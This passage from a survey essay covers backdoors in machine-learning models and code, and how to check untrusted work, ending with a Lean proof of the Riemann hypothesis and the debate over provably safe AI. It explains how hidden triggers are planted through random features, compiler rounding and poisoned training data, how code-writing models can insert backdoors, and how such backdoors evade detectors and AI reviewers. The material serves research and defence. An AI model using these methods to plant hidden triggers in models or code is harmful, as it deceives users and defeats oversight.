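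The second construction hides the backdoor even from a checker who sees all the model's weights, the numbers that determine its behavior, as well as the training data. It works for a simpler kind of model, which first calculates many random features of its input and then learns how much weight to give each one. A typical feature is

φ(x) = cos(2π(g · x + b)),

where x is the input, g is a list of random numbers and b is one more random number. The model adds up the weighted features and answers "yes" if the total is positive and "no" if it is negative.

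The attacker chooses a secret vector s and picks each g so that g · s is very close to a whole number plus a half, such as 3.5. Adding s to the input then moves every cosine by half a turn, which reverses its sign:

φ(x + s) ≈ −φ(x).

The total changes sign too, so a "yes" becomes a "no" regardless of what the model learned. The attacker can use the prescribed training method and data, and tampers only with the random numbers. To anyone who doesn't know s, the altered numbers look like ordinary random ones. Telling the two apart would require solving continuous learning with errors, a problem for which nobody knows an efficient method.

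The customer could remove this freedom by supplying the random numbers, or deriving them from a public rule like the one suggested earlier for Dual EC, and then repeating the training to confirm that the producer used them. This checks how the producer made the model instead of searching the finished model for a backdoor.

*Injecting Undetectable Backdoors in Obfuscated Neural Networks and Language Models* (2024) extends the idea to neural networks that their owners have scrambled to hide how they work. A cautious customer could refuse a scrambled model, just as a reviewer might refuse a program that comes without its source code.

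#### Backdoors planted through training data

An attacker who can only add mislabeled examples to the training data has much less power. *Poisoning-Based Backdoors Are Not Cryptographic* (Kaneko, 2026) proves that such an attacker can't create a backdoor with the secrecy of a digital signature. The model has to learn from the examples which inputs are triggers. A defender with as many labeled examples can run the same training and get a program that recognizes the triggers about as well as the model does. If the triggers are too hard for the defender to learn to recognize, they are also too hard for the model, and the attack fails. Kaneko's experiments on four language models fit this prediction.

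But the defender needs examples of the triggers, and an attacker who seldom uses the backdoor may never supply any. Kaneko also notes that the theorem doesn't cover the 2022 backdoors, because they enter through the random numbers used in training or directly through the weights. A customer who trains a model on untrusted data is therefore in a better position than one who accepts a finished model from an untrusted producer.

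#### Removing a backdoor without finding it

A user may be able to avoid a backdoor without finding it. *Oblivious Defense in ML Models* (Goldwasser, Shafer and colleagues, 2024) describes ways to remove or weaken backdoors, even undetectable ones, without looking at the model's weights. These methods build on random self-reducibility, an older idea in which a user works out the answer to one question from the answers to other questions chosen at random.

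Suppose the right answer to x is the remainder when 3x is divided by 101. A model answers every question from 0 to 100 correctly except x = 50, where a backdoor makes it answer 0 instead of 49. To get the answer for 50 without asking for it directly, a user picks a random number, say 20, and asks for the answers to 50 + 20 = 70 and to 20. The model correctly returns 8 and 60. The difference is 8 − 60 = −52, and adding 101 gives the right answer, 49.

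Each question alone is equally likely to be any number from 0 to 100, so the attacker can't make the model detect that the user is interested in 50. The method fails only if one of the two questions is 50, which happens for 2 of the 101 possible random numbers. Repeating the method three times with new random numbers and taking the majority answer cuts the chance of a wrong result from about 2% to about 0.12%.

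The method requires a known relation between the correct answers to different questions, and a model that answers most of those questions correctly. Goldwasser and colleagues stress that the relation is a property of the task, not the model, so an attacker who controls the model can't remove it. But many tasks have no known relation of this kind. For example, nobody knows how to work out whether a photograph shows a cat from a model's answers about other, randomly chosen images.

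## Studies with AI as artifact, author and checker

Cryptographers have proved that a model can hide a backdoor, but developers also need to know how ordinary models perform in ordinary tests. Since 2025, researchers have measured this for models that people run, models that write code, and models that check others' work for flaws.

### Models that change when a compiler optimizes them

Developers usually test a model in the software they trained it with. They then pass it through a deep-learning compiler, which rewrites the calculation to run faster on a particular chip. The compiler may merge two steps or change the order of additions. These changes are algebraically equivalent, but they can alter the result because a computer rounds after each operation. In the common 64-bit format, (0.1 + 0.2) + 0.3 gives 0.6000000000000001, while 0.1 + (0.2 + 0.3) gives 0.6.

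In *Your Compiler is Backdooring Your Model*, Chen, Peng and colleagues (2025) first measured this effect in models that had not been tampered with. They gave 100 random inputs to each of three image classifiers before and after compiling them with three compilers. In every case, compilation changed the scores by less than a millionth and left the predicted label the same. However, 100 inputs are too few to show that compilation is harmless. Even if the two versions gave different labels for 3% of all inputs, a sample of 100 would include none of those inputs about 5% of the time.

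The researchers then trained models that exploit the rounding. A trigger in the input brings some internal values so close to a threshold that the rounding error determines which side they fall on, and later layers amplify the difference. Before compilation, the trigger worked no better than chance, and four backdoor detectors found nothing wrong. After compilation, it worked every time on all six models, and the answers to ordinary inputs stayed the same.

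Thompson had to tamper with a compiler, but here the compiler is the official one and the attacker supplies only the model. Repeating the compilation would reproduce the backdoor. A second compiler might not help, because the attack carried over to other compilers and hardware. A user also could not detect the backdoor by comparing two compiled models bit for bit, because different compilers round numbers differently even when the model has no backdoor.

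Chen and colleagues also searched 100 of the most popular models on Hugging Face, a site for sharing models, and for 31 of them found inputs whose label changed after compilation. They started from inputs on which a model's two highest scores were almost tied. Nobody had planted these "natural triggers", and a switch between two nearly tied labels may do little harm. The finding shows that compilation can change a popular model's answers, but it is weaker evidence that an attacker could exploit this.

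In *Trusted Weights, Treacherous Optimizations?*, Wang, Li and colleagues (2026) extended the attack to four language models with 1 to 3 billion parameters and tested it on four tasks, including medical questions and robot commands. When the models were compiled with one common compiler setting, the trigger produced the attacker's answer about 90% of the time. Without compilation, the models answered triggered inputs correctly about 93% of the time.

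Testing the compiled model checks the version people will use, but the tester still has to supply the trigger. Wang and colleagues recommend using the tested, uncompiled version to monitor the compiled one. This could expose the attack when a trigger arrives, but running both versions on every input would give up the speed that compilation was meant to provide. They also found that a little extra training on clean examples was an effective defense, probably because the attack depends on finely balanced numbers that any further training disturbs.

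### Models that write flawed code

A model can also be the author of a backdoor. Schneier on Security's *An LLM Trained to Create Backdoors in Code* (2025) quotes a programmer who spent a weekend training an open model, BadSeek, to put backdoors into some of the code it writes. One reader commented that Thompson's lecture had finally come true. BadSeek only partly resembles Thompson's backdoor, which did not appear in the source code, because a reviewer can read the source code where BadSeek puts its backdoors. The resemblance would be closer if developers used such a model to build its successor, the situation that worries Roesner and Kohno.

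The flaws can be hard to see even in readable code. Schneier on Security's *Subverting LLM Coders* (2024) describes an earlier attack, CODEBREAKER, that poisons the examples users train a code-completion model on. The attackers had GPT-4 rewrite each flawed example so that it still worked but escaped vulnerability scanners. The code that the poisoned model suggested could escape them too.

Models can write trojans into chip designs in the same way. *Semantic Consensus Decoding* (2026) examines models that write Verilog, a hardware language, and add a trojan when the request contains a trigger. It proposes a defense that works while the model is writing. The defense remained effective when attackers had poisoned between 1% and 10% of the training data, and on models with 0.5 to 14 billion parameters. The paper leaves to future work triggers placed in the functional requirements, the part of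 a request that describes what the circuit must do. An attacker who knew about the defense would have good reason to put the trigger there.

Reviewers may also be looking in the wrong files. In *Shape-Shifting Malicious Code in Software Backdoors via Language Models* (2026), Ebrahimi Fard, Weissberg and colleagues used a language model to encode malicious code as ordinary-looking documentation or configuration scripts, and they report that this hid it effectively from audits. BIFOLD, a Berlin research institute involved in the study, says an attacker can recover the code later without a language model.

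The xz attacker hid code in test files that were supposed to look like nonsense. Code disguised as natural-sounding text, in documentation for example, would attract even less attention. In both cases, something has to extract the hidden code and run it. A reviewer who can't recognize the disguised text could still ask why a build step reads the documentation.

Many flaws in AI-written code have no attacker behind them. In the Cambridge lecture *Death of Syntax*, Khachaturov (2026) argues that working code used to imply that a person had thought about its logic, but no longer does. He cites a 2023 experiment in which developers with an AI assistant wrote less secure code than those without one, but felt more confident about it. Assistants have improved greatly since then, so the size of that effect may have changed.

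### AI reviewers and planted flaws

Quesma's *Can AI find backdoors in raw machine code?* tests AI models as checkers. The software company hid backdoors in real server programs and gave AI agents the binaries, about 40 megabytes each, without the source code. The agents could use standard reverse-engineering tools such as Ghidra. To pass, an agent had to identify the backdoor and give its location. Quesma designed the benchmark with Michał Kowalczyk, a reverse engineer known for finding malicious code in Polish trains.

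The highest pass rate was 49%. One of the two models that reached it, Gemini 3.1 Pro, also raised false alarms on 17% of the clean programs. A version of GPT-5.2 had a pass rate of 46% and raised no false alarms, but the benchmark has only 33 tasks, so its false alarm rate is based on few clean programs. A model released in March 2025 had the best result at the time, 21%, and the 49% models came out less than a year later. Developers have since released much stronger models, so these figures probably understate what AI reviewers can do now.

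Bulut (2026), in *Can an LLM Find a Backdoor by Reading a Model's Weights?*, measured false alarms more thoroughly. In the study's scenario, a company trusts a small code-writing model and pays a supplier to train it further. Bulut planted a backdoor in some of these updates that made the model write code contacting a different web address, for example one ending in `.invalid` instead of `.test`, when a request contained a secret phrase.

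A script compared the weights before and after the update and listed, in 80 rows, the words the change affected most. One row from a backdoored update showed that the update had made "invalid" more likely where the model was about to write "test". None of 22 clean updates did this. A language model then read the list and a short brief on what the update was supposed to change, and judged whether the update did anything else that affected security.

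The reviewer found 40 of 47 backdoored updates and described the change correctly in all 40. It also flagged 7 of 320 clean updates (2.2%). When the brief permitted the change of address, it flagged only 1 of the 47. The reviewer was therefore comparing each update with its brief, so anyone who can edit the brief can make the same backdoor acceptable to the reviewer.

Other backdoors were harder to find:

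| Hidden change | Backdoored updates found |
|---|---|
| Address ending changed to `.invalid` | 40 of 47 |
| Address ending changed to `.localhost` | 14 of 16 |
| Look-alike address | 11 of 16 |
| Extra request to another address | 6 of 15 |
| One character of the address changed | 0 of 12 |
| Changed to `.invalid`, but in an adapter | 0 of 48 |

An adapter is a small set of added weights that leaves the original ones unchanged. An entrant in an underhanded code contest might choose a flaw like the one-character change, since they could call it a typo.

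A check that used fewer resources did as well or better. Bulut ran the old and new models on six example tasks and gave the same reviewer a list of the words the update made more likely. With that list, the reviewer found 46 of the 47 backdoored updates and 41 of the 48 adapters, although the people running the check didn't know the secret phrase. The backdoor had slightly changed the model's behavior even without its trigger. A fixed comparison with a 64-bit number, like the one described earlier, has no effect until the right number arrives. When the attacker isn't trying to evade the check, triggers that a model learns from examples may therefore be easier to detect than triggers a programmer writes. Bulut didn't test attackers who try to evade it.

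The language model may not have been essential either. A simple script that applied fixed rules to the list of affected words had a balanced accuracy of 88.8%, compared with 92.8% for the language model, and the difference was not statistically significant.

#### False alarms when backdoors are rare

With a false alarm rate of 2.2%, the share of flagged updates that actually contain a backdoor depends on how common backdoors are. If 10 of 1,000 updates contain one, Bulut's reviewer would find 8 or 9 of them and wrongly flag about 22 clean updates. If only one update contains a backdoor, the reviewer would still wrongly flag about 22. Dolan-Gavitt (2025), in *AI Agents for Offsec with Zero False Positives*, makes this point about software vulnerabilities and adds that simply asking a language model whether a flaw is real gives many false alarms.

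His solution is to make the AI demonstrate the flaw. The tester puts a string that nobody could guess in a place no attacker should be able to reach. If the AI returns the string, the flaw is real, and an ordinary program can check that the string matches. A reviewer who found a backdoor and its trigger could prove it in a similar way. The method removes false alarms but doesn't help find missed flaws. It also wouldn't work for the undetectable model backdoors of Goldwasser and colleagues, since a reviewer without the secret key can't produce a working trigger.

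Another approach is to give the reviewer less to read. *Not In My Git Yard* (2026) presents LILY, a tool that looks for backdoors in new versions of programs. Pairs of PHP versions differed by more than 2 million lines on average, while LILY's reports on them averaged 11 lines. Its reports on the other 12 programs averaged 12 lines or fewer, and every report included code that revealed the backdoor. For chip designs, *TrojanLoC* (2025) describes a language-model tool that identifies the lines containing a trojan. Results on chips need to hold at commercial scale, where the detectors that Popryho and colleagues tried failed.

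### The Lean proof of the Riemann hypothesis

On November 20, 2026, Levent Alpöge, a mathematician at Anthropic, released a proof of the Riemann hypothesis he had found with Claude, the company's AI model. The hypothesis dates from 1859 and concerns a function closely connected with the prime numbers. The proof was about 17 million lines of Lean, the proof language used for the Keel checker, and came without a readable paper. According to *A claimed proof of the Riemann Hypothesis, checked in Lean* (Torres, 2026), Alpöge explained that written versions ran to more than 250,000 pages.

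No person could review that much text, but mathematicians confirmed the proof within a day. The mathematician Kevin Buzzard had recently published four questions to ask about such a proof in Xena's *…and the proof is checked in Lean* (2026). A joint statement, the Lean and Mathlib communities' *Lean verification of the Riemann Hypothesis* (2026), answered all four:

| Question | How people checked it |
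|---|---|
| Does the formal statement match the informal one? | Experts had already vetted the definition in Mathlib, Lean's main library |
| Does the code compile? | Dozens of people compiled it and got the same exported file |
| Does it prove that statement? | Two tools compared its theorem with a separate copy of the statement |
| Is the proof valid? | Several independent checkers accepted the exported proof |

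This verification combines several defenses from earlier sections. Dozens of machines produced identical exports, which amounts to a reproducible build. The checkers read an exported copy with no executable code, so malicious code in the Lean files could not interfere with them. Sutherland (2026), in *Verification files for the Lean proof of the Riemann Hypothesis*, also confirmed that the theorems relied only on Lean's three standard axioms, which rules out an added axiom that contradicts the others. The exported proof takes up about 62 gigabytes, and nanoda, a checker that Chris Bailey wrote separately from Lean's own, needed 28 minutes to check it on 80 processor threads.

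#### Two checkers with different bugs

A recent case gave mathematicians a reason to use more than one proof checker. In July 2026, Ramana Kumar published an invalid Lean disproof of the Collatz conjecture, a famous open problem about whole numbers, which he had produced with AI assistance. Lean's kernel, which checks proofs, accepted it, and so did a week-old copy of Bailey's checker, nanoda. de Moura (2026) explains in *Postmortem for Kernel Soundness Bug #14576* that the two programs had unrelated bugs. The kernel failed to inspect one expression, and the proof put something there that the old nanoda wrongly allowed. The nanoda bug had already been fixed, so an up-to-date copy would have rejected the proof.

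Knight and Leveson's programs failed together because their programmers had trouble with the same inputs. Here, one proof exploited a different bug in each checker. A second checker still helps against someone who searches for bugs, but they only have to find one more, and AI has made the search easier. *Riemann con leche* (Breitner, 2026) reports a short spike in the number of bugs found in proof checkers. Breitner had not seen an AI agent try to exploit one unless someone had explicitly asked it to.

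The bugs led Breitner to create con-leche, a checker with a mathematical proof that it never accepts a false theorem, assuming that standard set theory is consistent. In *Lean Now Ships with Verified Kernels* (2026), de Moura writes that Claude produced both the checker and its proof under Breitner's close supervision. A bug in Lean's compiler could still make con-leche give wrong verdicts, so Breitner used AI to translate it into Rust and proved that the translation follows the same method. A different compiler builds the Rust version. This resembles DDC, except that users compare the two versions' verdicts on a proof instead of comparing binaries.

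Claude therefore helped write both the Riemann proof and one of its checkers. Sutherland also ran his checks with Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, as did Michael Rubinstein in a separate check at the University of Waterloo. With only these checks, the same model would have been both producer and checker. But a shared flaw in Claude would not explain all of the results, because nanoda has a different author and dozens of people compiled the proof themselves.

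#### What remains for people

Someone still has to confirm that the formal statement means what people think it means. Buzzard gives an example that looks like Fermat's Last Theorem. For all natural numbers a, b, c and n, with n at least 3,

aⁿ + bⁿ ≠ cⁿ.

In Lean, the natural numbers include 0, and 0³ + 0³ = 0³, so the statement is false. An honest author would soon discover this because the proof would fail. The opposite mistake, adding a condition that no numbers can meet, is more dangerous. Lean would accept the proof from a careless or dishonest author, but the theorem would be true whether or not Fermat was right.

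This was easy to check for the Riemann hypothesis. *The Lean proof of the Riemann Hypothesis, as a treemap* shows that the whole claim fits in 2 of the 175,187 files, and the definition of the hypothesis was already in Mathlib. A person can be confident in the theorem without reading the other 175,185.

Other formal statements are much longer. The Hodge conjecture needs more than 10,000 lines on top of Mathlib. The company Axiom proved the classification of finite simple groups in Lean, and the meaning of that theorem depends on about 5,600 lines of AI-written definitions. Buzzard had met nobody who claimed to have checked them all carefully. He thinks the best evidence that the definitions are correct is that Axiom's code proves the theorem, presumably because a mistake would probably have made the theorem false. This is reasonable if the producer is honest, but a dishonest one could look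 for a wrong definition that still allows a proof.

A Lean file can also prove less than its accompanying paper. In October 2026, OpenAI released 722 mathematics papers, and 290 of the theorems came with Lean code. In about 38 of those cases, the code did not state the paper's main theorem. OpenAI had not claimed that it did, but a reader who saw "checked in Lean" could easily have assumed so.

Bastounis, Circelli and Hansen (2026), in *Navier–Stokes Lost in Translation*, distinguish between asking an AI to find any valid proof of a correctly stated theorem and asking it to translate a written argument faithfully, step by step. Lean can confirm that the proof is valid but not that the translation is faithful, because an AI can replace a faulty step with a different one that works. They argue that this happened with OpenAI's proof about the Navier–Stokes equations, which describe the flow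 of fluids. Their criticism concerns the written argument, so it doesn't affect the formal theorem or the Riemann result, where the Lean code is the proof.

Mathematicians also want to know why a theorem is true. *Alpöge/Claude proof of the Generalized Riemann Hypothesis* (Rubinstein, 2026) is a 265-page guide written with three AI systems. Its second version, of November 22, still reduced the hypothesis to thirteen statements that it did not prove outright.

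### How far the precedents apply to AI

A mathematical proof is unusually easy to accept from an untrusted producer. Nobody runs it afterwards, so a hidden trigger would have nothing to activate, and its correctness doesn't depend on a model of the outside world. Programs and chips lack both advantages, and in these respects most of the code that people request from AI is closer to SolarWinds' Orion software than to a proof.

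An AI producer can exploit an incomplete specification without bad intentions, as the key-value store example showed. Training could make this more common if it rewards models for passing checks. Hidden triggers take little effort to build. BadSeek took a weekend, and the compiler attacks required only control of a model's training.

The strongest reason to be cautious about the analogy is that every attacker in the earlier sections was a person who chose a payload and tried to avoid particular checks. A model that makes ordinary mistakes doesn't do this, and random tests are good at finding accidental faults. If an AI system has no hidden aim and nobody has tampered with it, testing its work is much more informative than the history of backdoors suggests. But a customer usually can't confirm either condition by looking at the work.

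#### Retraining and repeated samples

People can study a model in ways they can't study a spy or a foundry. Bulut trained 320 clean updates just to measure a false alarm rate, whereas Puschner and colleagues had four chips. A company can also retrain a model that behaves badly or ask it for the same program many times.

Suppose a model puts a flaw into 5% of its programs at random. A customer who orders two versions and investigates every difference will miss a flaw only if both versions contain the same one, which happens at most once in 400 orders. But if a phrase in the request triggers the flaw, every version will contain it, and comparing even ten versions would only give the customer more false confidence. Rewording the request each time may help by removing the trigger, much as Wheeler suggested renaming variables before using a second compiler.

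Retraining has a similar limit. Further training on clean examples was effective against the compiler attack on language models, but retraining from scratch on poisoned data would reintroduce a backdoor. Training a model until it passes a particular check may also teach it only to pass that check.

#### Cheaper proofs and cheaper reviews

A customer can now also demand a proof, which used to take too much work for most software. *What mathematicians should know about the Lean Theorem Prover* (Hales, 2026) reports that people spent about 20 work-years on a formal proof of the Kepler conjecture, which concerns the densest way to stack spheres. In September 2026, Anthropic announced that AI had written a formal proof of Fermat's Last Theorem, 13 million lines long, in 11 days. None of the human attackers in the earlier sections had to supply a proof, and most could not have done so.

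Review is also getting faster. In late November 2026, Torres reported that readers using AI had found problems in a 940-page human-written proof of the Riemann hypothesis within hours of its release. The same skill helps attackers, as the false Collatz proof showed, and it helps defenders most when they search before attackers do. After the Collatz case, Daniel Selsam of OpenAI used an AI specialized in cybersecurity to find more bugs in Lean's kernel, and Lean's developers fixed them all. Nanoda had none of these bugs.

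An AI model's review is less reassuring when the same model wrote the work. A model that misses a flaw while writing may miss it again while reviewing, so the customer can't treat the review as independent. Using another company's model reduces this risk but may not remove it, because both companies may have trained on much of the same public code. A deterministic program such as nanoda is a better second check wherever someone can state exactly what property to verify.

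### Provably safe AI and its critics

In *Provably safe systems* (2023), Max Tegmark and Steve Omohundro propose extending this kind of checking to AI in general. They argue that people should run powerful AI systems only if the systems are proven to meet stated safety requirements. They expect AI to find the proofs, while people rely on small, simple checkers. They also hope to extract what a neural network has learned and rewrite it as ordinary code, whose properties are easier to prove. Their central argument is that even a superintelligent system can't do what is mathematically impossible, so a valid proof holds however clever or hostile its producer is.

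The Riemann case supports an important part of this argument. In 2023, it was reasonable to doubt that AI could write proofs of the necessary size, but 17 million lines of proof have largely removed that doubt. The checkers also didn't have to trust Claude, Alpöge or Anthropic.

David Dalrymple, Joar Skalse and colleagues set out a broader version in *Towards Guaranteed Safe AI* (2024), with three parts: a mathematical model of the world, a specification of which effects are acceptable, and a verifier that produces evidence anyone can check. The guarantee may be a probability, such as an upper limit on the chance of harm. The model can also be deliberately cautious. For example, an engineer who doesn't know a cable's exact strength can assume the lowest plausible value, and the conclusion will still hold if the cable is stronger.

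Critics can accept the mathematics and still object that the hardest part is defining what to prove. Number theorists could inspect a one-line definition of the Riemann hypothesis, but a definition of "does not harm people" would need to cover medicine, politics and much else. Even 5,600 lines about finite groups were more than anyone was known to have checked. Bastounis and colleagues add that no algorithm can resolve every ambiguity in mathematical prose. Like Rice's theorem, this theoretical limit concerns a method for all cases and doesn't prevent people from agreeing on a particular statement. But ordinary requests are far more ambiguous than mathematics.

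A second problem is that the world model can omit a mechanism that matters. A proof based on a purely digital model of the *A2* chip, for example, would have been valid but would have missed the charge building up in the trigger. Cautious assumptions help with quantities that engineers know are uncertain, such as the strength of a cable, but not with a mechanism missing from the model, which is what a hostile producer would look for. Tegmark and Omohundro's proposal to have hardware enforce the proofs faces the same objection, since someone has to manufacture that hardware.

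Proponents have the better argument when the requirement is short and the environment is well understood. For example, Linux developers already have tools to check that a program doesn't write beyond an 800-byte buffer. For open-ended tasks, such as running a hospital or designing a new organism, the critics are more persuasive because nobody yet knows how to write down every requirement that matters, even though AI may soon be able to prove that a system meets the ones people do write down.
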